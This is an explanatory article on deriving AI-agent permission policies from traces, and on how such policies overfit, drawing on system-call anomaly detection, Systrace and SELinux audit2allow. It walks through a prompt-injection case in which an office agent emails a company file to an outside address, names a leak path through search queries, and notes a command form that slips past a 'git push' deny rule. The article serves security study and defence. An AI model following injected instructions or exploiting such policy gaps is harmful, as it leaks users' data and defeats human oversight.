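# Deriving agent permission policies from observed traces, and the risk of overfitting to past incidents

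## What a permission policy is, and two ways to write one from experience

A permission policy for an AI agent is a set of rules that allow an action, deny it, or send it to a person for a decision. People can write these rules by hand, from what they know of the job and its dangers, or derive them from experience using one of two opposite methods. One allows only actions that resemble recorded normal behaviour, and the other blocks actions that resemble recorded failures. Both methods derive rules for new cases from a limited number of past examples, and the rules may fit those examples too closely to be useful for anything else.

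### Agents, tool calls and the point of enforcement

An agent here is a language model that carries out tasks by calling tools in a loop. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes how a user states a task in ordinary language and the model then calls tools such as a web browser or an email search, using each result to help choose the next call. A tool call consists of a tool's name and its arguments, for instance `read_file("Cars/a.txt")`.

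A trace is the record of an agent's run. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) uses the word broadly to cover everything the agent generates or consumes during the run, including instructions, retrieved documents, memory operations and final responses. For permission policies, it is enough to define a trace more narrowly as the recorded sequence of actions in one run, with their arguments.

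The model produces text that names a tool and its arguments, and an ordinary program around the model reads that text, runs the tool and passes the result back. This program usually enforces the policy too. It compares each proposed call with the rules, then runs the call, returns a refusal to the model, or holds the call while a person decides. Claude Code, a coding agent from the AI company Anthropic, works this way. It checks each call against its deny rules, then its "ask" rules, then its allow rules, and applies the first rule that matches. Anthropic explains that instructions in a prompt shape what the model tries to do but do not change what the program allows.

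Christodorescu and colleagues argue for keeping the check outside the model because training a model never to do something makes it less likely to do it, but not impossible. If a check refuses unauthorised access 99% of the time, an attacker can try to exploit the remaining 1%. A fixed rule in an ordinary program gives the same answer every time.

Such a rule still covers only the calls it can match. An agent with a command line can fetch a web page without using its web tool, so a rule on the web tool alone does not cover every web request. Giving an agent a tool also does not settle which uses of it are acceptable. Zhou and Zhang (2026), in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, distinguish the tools an agent can invoke from what it is authorised to do with them.

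### Least privilege

The usual standard for a good policy is the principle of least privilege, which Saltzer and Schroeder set out in 1975 in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*. Under this principle, every program and every user should "operate using the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". This limits the damage that an accident or an error can do. The military rule of "need to know" is an example. Saltzer and Schroeder also recommend basing access decisions on permission rather than exclusion, so that the default is no access.

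Least privilege is harder to apply to agents than to ordinary software. A phone app does a fixed set of things, so its developer can declare the permissions it needs and others can check the declaration against the code. An agent has no such code to inspect, and its needs change with each request. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a user who asks a browser agent to comment on an issue in a software project, then to summarise the same issue. Commenting requires write access to one text box, while summarising requires no write access. Traces are attractive here because they are evidence of what the work has required.

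### An office agent and its record

Suppose a company runs an office agent that prepares short research summaries. The agent lists the files in a folder, reads some of them, searches the web and emails a summary to a colleague. (This example simplifies an application that *AgentGuardian* (Abaev, Klimov and colleagues, 2026) used to test a system for learning policies from traces.) Before enforcing a learned policy, the company only records the agent's normal behaviour for a while. This is called the staging period. The record contains seven calls.

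| No. | Recorded call | Judgement |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `list_files("Cars/")` | normal |
| 2 | `read_file("Cars/a.txt")` | normal |
| 3 | `read_file("Cars/b.txt")` | normal |
| 4 | `search_web("electric car sales")` | normal |
| 5 | `send_email(to="ana@firm.example")` | normal |
| 6 | `send_email(to="ben@firm.example")` | normal |
| 7 | `send_email(to="drop@outside.example")` | failure |

Call 7 resulted from a prompt injection, meaning instructions that an attacker plants in material the agent will read. The agent opened a web page with instructions to send the contents of `Cars/b.txt` to an outside address, and followed them.

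We could write two policies from this record. An allowlist names the permitted actions and denies everything else, so it is also called default-deny; here it would permit calls 1 to 6. The idea of learning such a list from recorded behaviour comes from anomaly detection in computer security, which treats departures from the record as suspect. A denylist names the forbidden actions and allows everything else, so it is also called default-permit; here it would forbid call 7. Older texts use the terms whitelist and blacklist. *Guide to Application Whitelisting* (Sedgewick, Souppaya and Scarfone, 2015), from the US standards institute NIST, adds a graylist for items that nobody has yet classified as benign or malicious, which a system may handle by asking the user.

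Neither list is much use if taken literally. The allowlist would stop the agent from reading `Cars/c.txt` if someone added that file tomorrow, and from making any web search except the one about electric car sales. An attacker could get around the denylist by opening a new mailbox. Both lists therefore need a generalisation step, which turns the recorded examples into rules that cover more cases, and how far to generalise is an open choice.

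| Width of the rule | Allow rule from `read_file("Cars/a.txt")` | Deny rule from the email to `drop@outside.example` |
|---|---|---|
| Exact | that file | that address |
| Narrow | every text file in `Cars/` | every address at `outside.example` |
| Broad | every text file | every address outside the company |
| Broadest | every file | every email |

The record contradicts only one of these rules, the ban on every email, because calls 5 and 6 were legitimate emails. The other rules all fit the record but would have very different effects. Permission to read every text file would include `HR/salaries.txt`. A ban on every outside address would stop the agent from sending a summary to a client, which never happened during staging but which the company may want next month. Whoever picks a rule has to use knowledge from outside the record, such as what the folders are for and who counts as a colleague,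 or leave the choice to a learning method's built-in biases.

Existing products routinely make this choice, often on very little evidence. When a user of Claude Code approves the command `npm test`, which runs a project's tests, they can also choose not to be asked again about `npm test *`, where the star stands for any text, so approving one command can permit a whole family of them. Sedgewick and colleagues describe the same dilemma for rules about which programs may run on a computer. A rule that permits everything in a given folder needs little upkeep, but it also allows any malicious file placed there to run, unless strict controls govern who can write to the folder. A rule based on a cryptographic hash, a value computed from a file's exact contents, permits only that file, so it stops working as soon as the vendor issues a patch.

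The breadth of a rule is also easy to misjudge. Abaev and colleagues print a learned rule for a file-reading tool with this pattern for permitted paths: `\./(Cars/[^\s]*|AI/ai\-[^\s]*\-2025|[^\s]*)\.txt`. The vertical bars separate alternatives, and the last one, `[^\s]*`, matches any string without spaces, so the pattern as printed permits `./HR/salaries.txt`. Yet they describe the rule as limiting the agent to text files in two folders, `Cars` and `AI`.

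### The two kinds of error, in sets

Let *U* be all the actions the agent could take, *N* the actions its legitimate work needs, and *H* the harmful ones. Let *P* be the recorded normal actions (calls 1 to 6) and *F* the recorded failures (call 7). The generalisation step is an operator *g* that takes a set of recorded actions and returns a set that is usually larger. In practice each list has its own operator, but we use *g* for both.

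The allowlist permits only *g*(*P*), while the denylist permits everything in *U* except *g*(*F*). Each can make two kinds of error. A false acceptance is a harmful action that the policy permits, and a false rejection is a legitimate action that it blocks. The errors are given below, where ∩ means what two sets share and a minus sign means what remains of the first set after removing the second.

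| | Allowlist | Denylist |
|---|---|---|
| Permitted actions | *g*(*P*) | *U* − *g*(*F*) |
| False acceptances | *H* ∩ *g*(*P*) | *H* − *g*(*F*) |
| False rejections | *N* − *g*(*P*) | *N* ∩ *g*(*F*) |

Suppose the company uses an allowlist that permits text files in `Cars/`, any web search, and email to any company address. A request for a summary about boats would cause a false rejection because the files are in another folder. The allowlist could also cause a false acceptance. Because it permits every search query, an injected instruction could make the agent paste the contents of `Cars/b.txt` into one. A denylist that blocks all outside email addresses would allow the boats task and block the email to the client, but it would also fail to stop the leak through web search.

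Widening *g* gives an allowlist fewer false rejections but more false acceptances, or at best the same number. It has the opposite effect on a denylist, so adding a deny rule after an incident can block legitimate actions. *VEPA* (2026), which concerns rules that evolve as an agent runs, describes every update as a trade-off between repairing new failures and preserving behaviour that the policy already handles correctly.

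Even if *g*(*P*) were exactly *N* and *g*(*F*) exactly *H*, so that neither list made an error, the allowlist would block actions that are neither needed nor harmful, such as reading the canteen menu, while the denylist would allow them. The principle of least privilege favors the allowlist, because access that nobody needs can still do damage when something goes wrong.

*N* and *H* also depend on what counts as an action. Opening `HR/salaries.txt` may be necessary for a payroll task and harmful during a research summary. If the policy is based only on the tool and the file path, these are the same action, so *N* and *H* overlap and any rule will be wrong in one of the two situations. A policy also based on the task or the earlier calls can separate them, but then there are many more distinct actions to learn about from the same record.

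Nobody can observe *N* or *H* in full, only *P* and *F*. Researchers who derive access rules for human users from logs faced this problem well before language-model agents existed. *Mining Attribute-based Access Control Policies* (2013) defines the two errors as over-assignment, where a user has a permission they should not have, and under-assignment, where a user lacks one they should have. Logs give only a lower bound on what people may do, because nobody uses every permission while the logging runs. *Mining Attribute-Based Access Control Policies from Logs* (2014) therefore accepts that a derived policy must grant some permissions beyond those in the log, "but not too many". The gap can be very large. *The Next 700 Policy Miners* (2019) mentions logs that hold barely 7% of all possible requests.

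*P* may also contain actions that do not belong there. Abaev and colleagues assume that nothing misleading happens during staging, and suggest discarding rare inputs or having staff review them. If call 7 had gone unnoticed, it would have entered the record as normal, and the allowlist would have permitted it from then on. A satisfactory result is also not enough to make a call normal. Zhou and Zhang point out that an agent can complete its task while exceeding the authority the user gave it, for example by sending records to an outside service for processing when it could have processed them locally.

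People report these errors as rates. Abaev and colleagues divide the number of false acceptances by the number of illegitimate attempts, and the number of false rejections by the number of benign samples. These rates depend on which attempts and samples the testers chose, and estimating them properly is a separate statistical problem.

People are also more likely to notice when a policy wrongly refuses an action than when it wrongly allows one. Saltzer and Schroeder observed that a mistake in a mechanism based on explicit permission tends to refuse access, which users soon notice, whereas a mistake in a mechanism based on exclusion tends to allow access, which can go unnoticed in normal use. For example, an employee whose boats summary fails will complain the same day, but a leak to an address that nobody thought to list produces no error message.

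### Overfitting

Overfitting means matching the recorded examples so closely, or relying on such accidental features of them, that the rules fail on new cases. An overfitted allowlist is too tight. It permits `Cars/a.txt` and `Cars/b.txt` but blocks `Cars/c.txt`, which hinders new but legitimate work. In the notation, *g*(*P*) is hardly larger than *P*, and *N* − *g*(*P*) is large.

An overfitted denylist is too narrow. Its rules are signatures, each matching one known attack or a small family of attacks, so it misses variants of failures already in the record. In Claude Code, for example, a deny rule for commands that begin with `git push`, which uploads code to a shared repository, does not match `git -C . push`, which does the same thing. Anthropic warns that such a rule covers the form of a command that the model usually produces and is not a security boundary around the program. Novel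 misbehaviour, meaning harm of a kind absent from the record, is harder to block than a variant because even sensibly broadened rules may not cover it.

Overfitting therefore makes an allowlist block too much and a denylist allow too much. Sedgewick and colleagues caution that frequently blocking authorised software can seriously affect an organisation's work.

A rule can also fail because it depends on accidental features of the log. The file-reading rule that Abaev and colleagues print also restricts access to between 07:33:09 and 20:25:33, because their method takes the earliest and latest times in the log as limits. A restriction to working hours may be sensible, but that exact start time reflects only when somebody happened to start work. Deny rules can pick up coincidences in the same way. Suppose the office agent had searched for battery prices shortly before call 7. A rule that blocks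 any email after a search about batteries would stop the one recorded failure and none of the six normal calls. But it would also block every future summary about batteries, and it would let the same injection through from a page about tyres. Making this rule wider or narrower would not help, because it depends on the wrong property of the example. A single recorded failure gives little evidence of which property is the right one. Even the outside address is only a proxy for what went wrong, which was that the agent followed an instruction from a stranger's web page and sent a company file to someone who had no business receiving it.

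## Learning normal behaviour from sequences of actions

The rules discussed so far apply to one action at a time. A trace also records the order of actions, so a policy can be based on which sequences are normal. *A Sense of Self for Unix Processes* (Forrest, Hofmeyr and colleagues, 1996) introduced an early and influential method of this kind, intended to detect attacks on Unix programs without knowing beforehand what the attacks would look like. The method was inspired by the immune system, which distinguishes the body's own molecules from foreign ones.

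The actions in this case are system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file, read data, start another program and so on. A program does damage through these calls, so they are a natural place to look for it. Forrest and colleagues studied programs that run with full administrative privileges, because an attacker gains most from them and because they do a narrow range of things. They kept the name of each call and discarded its arguments, so opening a mail queue and opening the password file both count as `open`. (Later tools such as Systrace keep the arguments.)

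AI agents also leave traces of this kind, since their tools run as ordinary programs. King, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security*, recorded the system calls of 4,047 agent sessions and found that these calls alone helped to tell malicious sessions from benign ones. They trained their detectors on labelled examples of both kinds, whereas the 1996 method learns from normal behaviour only.

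### Counting mismatches

During the staging period, a window slides along the trace. For each call, the method notes which calls follow it at distance 1, at distance 2 and so on, up to a distance *k*. Forrest and colleagues illustrate this with *k* = 3 and a trace of eight calls:

`open, read, mmap, mmap, open, getrlimit, mmap, close`

The trace produces the following database.

| Call | Distance 1 | Distance 2 | Distance 3 |
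|---|---|---|---|
| `open` | `read`, `getrlimit` | `mmap` | `mmap`, `close` |
| `read` | `mmap` | `mmap` | `open` |
| `mmap` | `mmap`, `open`, `close` | `open`, `getrlimit` | `getrlimit`, `mmap` |
| `getrlimit` | `mmap` | `close` | |
| `close` | | | |

Now suppose a new trace differs in one place, with `open` instead of `mmap` as the fourth call:

`open, read, mmap, open, open, getrlimit, mmap, close`

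Four pairs in this trace are missing from the database:

- `open` followed by `open` at distance 3
- `read` followed by `open` at distance 2
- `open` followed by `open` at distance 1
- `open` followed by `getrlimit` at distance 2

The changed call belongs to six pairs, two of which are already in the database, leaving four mismatches. A trace of length *L* has *k*(*L* − (*k* + 1)/2) pairs to check, which here is 3 × (8 − 2) = 18, so the mismatch rate is 4/18, or 22%.

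Forrest and colleagues chose `sendmail`, a large and complicated mail program, for a realistic test. They wrote 112 messages to exercise its normal uses, varying the length and content of the mail, sending it in bursts, forwarding it and making it bounce. The messages generated more than 1.5 million system calls, but with a window of six, the database held only about 1,500 entries, each a pair of calls at a given distance. A plot of the first 10,000 calls shows almost no new entries after about 3,000 calls.

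They then traced several attacks and errors. The results below are for a window of six, with a separate database for the attack on the printing program `lpr`.

| Trace | Mismatches | Mismatch rate |
|---|---|---|
| Attack that appends a message to a protected file | 95 | 4.1% |
| Attack that overflows a buffer through the system log (four runs) | 137 to 470 | 1.5% to 4.2% |
| "Decode" attack, which overwrites files by email | 24 | 0.3% |
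| Attack on `lpr` that replaces a file's contents | 12 | 1.4% |
| Two attacks that failed | 36 and 157 | 0.4% and 1.7% |
| Mail caught in a forwarding loop, a harmless mistake | 58 | 1.8% |

Every attack produced mismatches, including attacks that nobody had used to build the database. But the mismatch rate does not separate attacks from accidents, since the forwarding loop's rate was six times as high as the decode attack's. Forrest and colleagues reported the numbers without choosing a threshold for raising an alarm. Normal mail produced no mismatches, but only because they had kept adding the mismatches from new normal messages to the database. The experiment therefore could not show how often the method would raise a false alarm, which is equivalent to a false rejection in a policy that blocks actions.

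### Constructed and live traces

The 112 messages are an example of constructed traces, which people make by exercising a program in every way they can think of. Live traces are recorded while people use the program for their ordinary work. Hofmeyr, Forrest and Somayaji (1998) tried both in *Intrusion Detection using Sequences of System Calls*. Constructed traces are easy to repeat and to keep free of attacks, but they contain only the variations their makers thought of. Live traces contain what users do, but an attack during recording may be included as normal behaviour, and nobody knows when the record is complete. As the record grows, it also takes in rare behaviour, some of which may resemble an attack.

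For the live test, Hofmeyr and colleagues recorded `lpr` during 2,766 print jobs on 77 machines at MIT over two weeks, and 1,234 on one machine at the University of New Mexico over 13 weeks. They could keep one known attack out of the record because it needs about a thousand print jobs in close succession, and the system never handled more than 200 in a day. They acknowledge that this precaution does not exclude attacks they did not know about.

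The New Mexico and MIT sites ran the same printing program on the same operating system, yet only 141 sequences of calls appeared in both records. These made up 40% of the New Mexico sequences and 29% of the MIT sequences. A policy learned at one site would have raised alarms about ordinary printing at the other.

When Hofmeyr and colleagues learned from 700 of the MIT jobs and tested on the rest, they got about one false alarm per 100 jobs, or two a day. Doubling the number of jobs in the record halved the rate. Some alarms came from real faults, such as a print job so large that the machine ran out of disk space. Others came from legitimate but uncommon habits, such as printing a file through a symbolic link, which is a file that points to another.

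How long to record remains a matter of judgement. Warrender, Forrest and Pearlmutter, in *Detecting Intrusions Using System Calls* (1999), stopped once the record's average growth had stayed below one new sequence per ten traces for at least ten traces. This rule detects when a record has almost stopped growing, but the record could still be missing a task that people do once a year.

Warrender and colleagues also tested the idea that rare behaviour is suspicious. One of their methods treated any sequence that made up less than 0.001% of the normal record as if it were absent, and it consistently did worse than the others they compared. This result matters for AI agents too, because Abaev and colleagues suggest cleaning up a staging record by discarding rare inputs, some of which will be legitimate work.

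### Two ways to generalise from the same record

A policy that accepted only complete recorded traces would reject almost every new run, since a complicated program seldom makes exactly the same long series of calls twice. Cutting traces into short windows makes the policy more general, because a new run can pass if all its windows appear in the recorded traces. How far the policy generalises depends on how the method stores the windows.

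The 1996 method stores lookahead pairs, as in the database above. Each pair records a call, a later call and the distance between them. By 1998 the New Mexico group had switched to full sequences, storing each window whole and accepting only an exact match. Most later researchers followed them. *Lookahead Pairs and Full Sequences* (Inoue and Somayaji, 2007) was the first direct comparison of the two methods.

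The difference is easy to see with three short, invented traces from the office agent in the previous section, keeping only the names of its tools:

1. `read, read, email`
2. `list, search, email`
3. `read, search, read`

With a window of three calls, full sequences accept only these three runs. Lookahead pairs also accept `read, read, read` and `read, search, email`. No trace contains `read, search, email`, but each of its pairs occurs in a trace at the same spacing. Trace 3 has `search` directly after `read`, trace 2 has `email` directly after `search`, and trace 1 has `email` two steps after `read`.

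Accepting `read, read, read` avoids a false alarm when a summary needs three files. The run `read, search, email` may also be an ordinary summary, or it may come from an agent that read a company file, found an injected instruction in its search results and emailed the file to a stranger. Matching on lookahead pairs accepts both new runs, while matching on full sequences flags both until someone adds them to the record.

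Inoue and Somayaji measured the effect on several of the New Mexico recordings. Their most detailed results are for `named`, a name server, which translates internet names into numerical addresses. They learned its normal behaviour from 21 days of recordings, about 6.3 million calls, and counted false alarms over another 12 days.

| Window length | False alarms a day, lookahead pairs | False alarms a day, full sequences | Windows accepted, lookahead pairs | Windows accepted, full sequences |
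|---|---|---|---|---|
| 4 | 0 | 1.03 | 27,600 | 516 |
| 6 | 0.26 | 9.07 | 9.42 million | 958 |
| 10 | 0.94 | 34.24 | 2.67 trillion | 2,440 |
| 32 | 7.11 | 1,534 | about 10⁴⁴ | 48,900 |

With a window of six, lookahead pairs reduced false alarms from nine a day to about one every four days, because they accepted nearly 10,000 times as many windows, almost none of which had been recorded. In the notation of the previous section, they apply a wider *g* to the same *P*, which risks more false acceptances.

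The figure of 9.42 million overstates how much new behaviour could pass unnoticed, because it counts each window in isolation. In a small example from Inoue and Somayaji, lookahead pairs accept eight four-call windows ending in `read`, and the program had produced two of them. In a running program, each of the other six would have caused an alarm at an earlier call, but the office agent's `read, search, email` would cause no earlier alarm.

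Accepting more windows also does not guarantee fewer false alarms. On a recording of `lpr`, again with a window of six, lookahead pairs accepted 17.5 million windows and full sequences accepted only 604, yet both methods raised about 1.2 false alarms per 10,000 calls. Inoue and Somayaji attribute this to a small training record drawn from many different machines. Presumably, new print jobs produced few of the millions of extra combinations.

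The effect on missed attacks is much harder to measure. Earlier tests by the New Mexico group, with windows of six to ten, found the two methods about equally good at detecting attacks, but those tests used a small number of known attacks, whereas the false alarm rates come from millions of normal calls. Inoue and Somayaji conclude that lookahead pairs are the better method, though they concede that the pairs are less sensitive to some attacks and leave more room for intruders who stay within recorded behaviour.

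Hofmeyr and colleagues generalised in another way, by tolerating small differences. They compared each new sequence of ten calls with the most similar recorded sequence and counted the positions in which the two differed. The most unusual sequence in the `lpr` attack differed in four positions, so they set the alarm to trigger at four differences, the highest threshold that would catch it. Their rate of one false alarm per 100 jobs therefore depends on a tolerance fitted to a single attack. An attack whose sequences never differed in more than three positions would have gone undetected.

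They were more willing to miss attacks than to raise false alarms, because adding defences reduces the number of missed attacks but increases the number of false alarms. If an intruder must get past *n* independent defences, each of which misses an attack with probability *p*, the probability that all of them miss it is *p*ⁿ. Three such defences that each miss 10% of attacks together miss only 0.1%, but if each raises one false alarm a day, staff must deal with three a day. This argument favours accepting a wide range of behaviour as normal only if the defences fail independently, and an attack made up of ordinary-looking actions may get past several of them for the same reason.

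A milder response can also make false alarms less disruptive. The Linux extension pH, which uses lookahead pairs, delays unusual system calls instead of refusing them. Forrest, Hofmeyr and Somayaji explain in *The Evolution of System-call Monitoring* (2008) that the delay is imperceptible for an isolated unusual call but grows exponentially when many occur together. Most false alarms therefore barely affect the user, while real attacks, which tend to produce clusters of unusual calls, can stall for hours or days.

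### The length of the window

A longer window makes a policy stricter, because a new run must match the record over a longer stretch. For the name server, lengthening the window from six to 32 raised the false alarms from full sequences from nine a day to more than one a minute. The number of accepted windows in the table rises with length, but the number of possible windows rises much faster, so the policy accepts a smaller share of them. Between lengths six and ten, each extra position multiplied the number of windows that lookahead pairs accept by about 23, and the number of possible windows by around 200, which is roughly how many different system calls such systems have.

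Inoue and Somayaji found that ignoring some of the positions in a long window avoided most of its false alarms. With a window of 20 in which only six randomly chosen positions counted, the full-sequence method raised 2.2 false alarms a day, compared with 307 when all 20 counted and nine with an unbroken window of six. They suspect that the gaps allow substitutions much as lookahead pairs do, but leave the question open. On the one attack they tried, the gaps made little difference to the number of alarms.

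Short windows have a different weakness. With a window of two, even a detector that compares full sequences would accept `read, search, email`, because the office agent's three traces contain both `read, search` and `search, email`. Tan and Maxion, in *Why 6?* (2002), call such a run a minimal foreign sequence, meaning one that is absent from the record although every shorter piece of it is present. They generated a million symbols of artificial training data and inserted minimal foreign sequences of two to nine symbols into separate test data. Then they ran a full-sequence detector with windows of two to 15. It detected the insertion whenever the window was at least as long as the inserted sequence, and never when it was shorter.

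Hofmeyr and colleagues had found that full sequences could detect the decode attack only with a window of at least six, and other researchers had adopted six as a standard length without knowing why it worked. Tan and Maxion traced the number to the sequence `fork, connect, close, close, connect, open` in one recording of the decode attack. That was the only attack recording with no shorter foreign sequence. Without that recording, a shorter window would have caught every attack in the collection, so the standard length came from a single incident.

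More normal data would not have revealed the right length either. A foreign sequence is by definition absent from the normal record, so Tan and Maxion conclude that it may be impossible to choose the best window in advance from normal behaviour alone. Choosing a very long window to be safe has drawbacks. They state that an overlong window uses more computing power but does not reduce accuracy, which is true for detecting attacks but not for the false alarms that Inoue and Somayaji counted. In the comparison by Warrender and colleagues, full sequences did slightly better on average with a window of six than with a window of ten, even though they learned from less data with the shorter window. This may be because shorter sequences generalise better.

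It is also uncertain whether the six-call sequence was related to the decode attack. Tan and Maxion knew of no analysis that linked the foreign sequences in these recordings to the attacks. They acknowledge that this one may have been ordinary behaviour missing from too small a training record, in which case the standard window length was based on a false alarm.

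## Turning logs into allow rules in operating systems and clouds

The sequence detectors record only the names of system calls. *Improving Host Security with System Call Policies* (Provos, 2003) introduced Systrace, which also records their arguments. Systrace turns recorded calls into rules and blocks any call that no rule permits.

### Systrace

A Systrace policy has an ordered list of statements for each system call. A statement pairs a condition on the call's arguments with an action, which is to permit the call, deny it or ask the user. Systrace applies the first statement whose condition holds. Provos prints part of the policy for `named`, the name server:

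| Statement | What it permits |
|---|---|
| `native-accept: permit` | Accepting any incoming connection |
| `native-chdir: filename eq "/namedb" then permit` | Moving to the directory `/namedb` |
| `native-connect: sockaddr eq "/dev/log" then permit` | Connecting to the system log |
| `native-bind: sockaddr match "inet-*:53" then permit` | Listening for name requests on any network interface |

The operator `eq` requires an exact match, while `match` accepts any text in place of the star. Systrace builds and uses such a policy as follows:

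1. The user runs the program, and Systrace intercepts its system calls.
2. Systrace translates the arguments into a standard readable form. For example, it replaces a relative file name with the full path.
3. It checks the call against the policy written so far.
4. If no statement covers the call, Systrace appends one that permits it.
5. After training, Systrace enforces the policy. It either asks the user about a call that no statement covers, or denies the call, logs it and returns an error to the program.

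When Systrace prompts the user about a system call, the user can allow or deny that one call, stop the program, or add a policy statement that covers the call from then on.

The method assumes that the program contains no malicious code and handles only benign data during training. Provos also assumes that a person will be available to handle whatever the training run missed, since it may be impossible to exercise every path through a program. The user has to judge whether an unfamiliar call comes from a new path in the program or from an intruder who has taken it over.

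Policies for some programs also needed editing by hand, because the programs choose random names for their temporary files. In Provos's example, a program asks for a file named `/tmp/conf` plus six random characters and gets `/tmp/confJ31A69`. Systrace then writes a rule for that exact name, which is useless on the next run. The corrected rule permits writing to `/tmp/conf*`. Whoever edits the rule has to know how the program picks its names, because a single run cannot show which characters are random. The new rule also covers any other file whose path starts with `/tmp/conf`, whether or not this program created it.

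Systrace also generalises less visibly, by grouping system calls with similar functions to keep policies short. Checking a file's status and opening it for reading both count as `fsread`, so a program that during training only checked whether a file existed may later read its contents.

The company monkey.org, which provided Unix accounts, used Systrace to confine more than 200 users and generated policies for about 250 programs. On average, a policy permitted 71 different system calls out of the several hundred that Unix systems usually support. This leaves an intruder who takes over a program with far fewer calls to exploit, but Provos acknowledges that the intruder can still misuse the program's legitimate functions. Over two months, the account with the most policy violations was the web server's, because it kept trying to run scripts that users had written. Running users' scripts can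 be a normal part of a web server's job, so a large number of denials may simply mean that a policy is too tight. (The operating system OpenBSD, which once included Systrace, later replaced it with permissions that programs declare for themselves.)

### SELinux and audit2allow

SELinux, a security system for Linux, labels every process and file with a type, and its rules refer to these types instead of individual file names. Each rule allows processes of one type to perform certain operations on objects of another. For example, `allow app app_data_file:file {open read}` lets processes of type `app` open and read files of type `app_data_file`. SELinux denies any operation that no rule allows.

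A short rule can therefore grant many permissions, especially as rules can also name whole groups of types. In *CASPR*, Xiao, Wang and colleagues (2025) counted 99,054 distinct rules in the standard policy of CentOS 7, a version of Linux. Those rules expand to about 173.5 million permissions when each combination of process type, object type and operation is counted separately.

SELinux can run in a permissive mode, which is useful for staging because it logs violations without blocking them. Administrators writing a policy for one new program once had to make the whole machine permissive. Red Hat's *Fixing Problems* explains that they can now make a single type of process permissive and keep the rest of the system protected.

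A tool called audit2allow converts logged denials into allow rules. In Red Hat's example, SELinux has stopped the program `certwatch` from writing to a directory. The tool uses some parts of the log message and discards others:

| Part of the log message | Value | Used in the rule? |
|---|---|---|
| Type of the process | `certwatch_t` | yes |
| Type of the object | `var_t` | yes |
| Kind of object | `dir` (a directory) | yes |
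| Denied operation | `write` | yes |
| Name of the directory | `cache` | no |

The result is `allow certwatch_t var_t:dir write;`. The program needed to write to one directory, `cache`, but the rule allows it to write to every directory of type `var_t`. According to Xiao and colleagues, these include `/var` itself, one of the main system directories. The generalisation comes from the file labels, which somebody assigned earlier for other reasons.

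Sometimes SELinux denies access because a file has the wrong label. Red Hat describes a web server that was blocked from a file in its own web directory because the file was labelled `samba_share_t`, a type meant for files shared over a network. A diagnostic tool suggested three remedies and gave each a confidence score: 92.2 for restoring the file's proper label, 7.83 for relabelling it as public content, and 1.41 for creating an allow rule with audit2allow. The allow rule would have fixed the problem with this one file by giving the web server the same access to every file labelled `samba_share_t`.

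Red Hat therefore warns administrators not to use audit2allow as their first option. They should first check for a wrong label, then for a change to the program's configuration that SELinux has not been configured to match. If a rule is missing, the cause is usually a bug in the policy, which they should report. Red Hat's *Allowing Access* adds that the generated rules "may allow more access than required" and recommends posting them to a mailing list for review.

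### Why repeated exceptions widen a policy

Suppose a policy permits a set of actions *A* and denies an action *d*. After someone converts the denial into a rule, the policy permits *A* ∪ *g*({*d*}), where ∪ means everything in either set and *g* extends the permission to all objects of the same type. The new set contains everything in *A*, so repeating the procedure never removes a permission. Narrowing the policy requires a separate process for finding and removing rules.

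A single task can require several allow rules. In Red Hat's example, SELinux denies the web server's request for a file's status, which programs check before reading a file, and logs the denial. In permissive mode, SELinux also logs a request to read the file. An administrator who allowed only the first request and kept SELinux in enforcing mode would soon see the read request denied too.

The log can also contain requests for access that a program does not need. Red Hat notes that programs often probe for more access than their work requires, and that the standard policy denies many of these requests without logging them. Administrators can choose to log these denials when investigating a fault. If they then converted every denial into an allow rule, they would grant access that the program had managed without.

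SELinux guards against such widening with `neverallow` rules, which specify access that no allow rule may grant. A policy containing a conflicting allow rule will not compile, but this helps only if somebody has foreseen the dangerous access.

### Separating attacks from ordinary denials

Converting denials into rules is especially risky when some of the denied requests come from attackers. *EASEAndroid* (Wang, Enck and colleagues, 2015) analysed 1.3 million audit logs, which mixed benign and malicious accesses, from SEAndroid, the version of SELinux used on Android phones. It learned 2,518 new access patterns, generated 331 new rules, and identified eight categories of attack pattern, two of them new.

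The lead author's dissertation, *Automatic Generation, Refinement and Analysis of Security Policies* (Wang, 2016), gives the fullest account. The logs came from Samsung devices in everyday use during 2014 and contained more than 14 million denials. Removing duplicates and grouping similar events left 3,530 access patterns, each describing a program, an operation and an object, with their labels.

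EASEAndroid uses semi-supervised learning, which extends a small number of known classifications to a large number of unclassified examples. It started with the phones' existing policy and 17 malicious patterns from nine known attack programs. Three learners then compared the unknown patterns with this knowledge:

- The nearest-neighbour learner looks at who performs an action. If enough of the programs that perform an unfamiliar action are known to be malicious, it classifies the action as malicious too. It also works in reverse, classifying an unfamiliar program by its known actions.
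- The distance learner compares a pattern with existing rules. If a rule allows a program to write to a file, a request to append to the same file is close to that rule and probably benign. A pattern close to a `neverallow` rule is probably malicious.
- The co-occurrence learner looks for patterns that appear within ten minutes of each other, since an attack often takes several steps. For patterns *i* and *j*, it divides the number of times they occur together by the total number of times *i* occurs. If *i* is unknown and usually accompanies known malicious patterns, the learner classifies it as malicious.

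EASEAndroid uses each newly classified pattern as evidence in the next round. With strict thresholds, it accepts a classification from any one learner. With looser thresholds, it requires two learners to produce the same classification and the third not to produce a conflicting one, and a person should check the results.

By the end of the year, EASEAndroid had correctly classified 2,182 patterns as malicious and 336 as benign, misclassified 106, and left 906 undecided. Wang judged correctness by comparing the results with a later human-written policy and consulting experienced analysts. At least 62% of the distinct patterns were therefore malicious, and running audit2allow on the whole log would have produced rules permitting them.

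Stricter thresholds reduced errors but left more patterns undecided:

| Threshold for neighbours and co-occurrence | Undecided | Wrong among those called malicious | Wrong among those called benign |
|---|---|---|---|
| 55% | 8.8% | 37.0% | 41.4% |
| 65% | 18.2% | 11.3% | 28.7% |
| 75% | 23.4% | 8.7% | 11.1% |
| 85% | 25.7% | 3.2% | 9.2% |
| 95% | 37.7% | 2.7% | 0% |

The last column matters most for an allowlist's security, because a malicious pattern classified as benign can become a permission. Errors also spread, since the system learns from its own output. By February it had wrongly classified four patterns as malicious. The nearest-neighbour learner used them to misclassify others, and by December there were 72.

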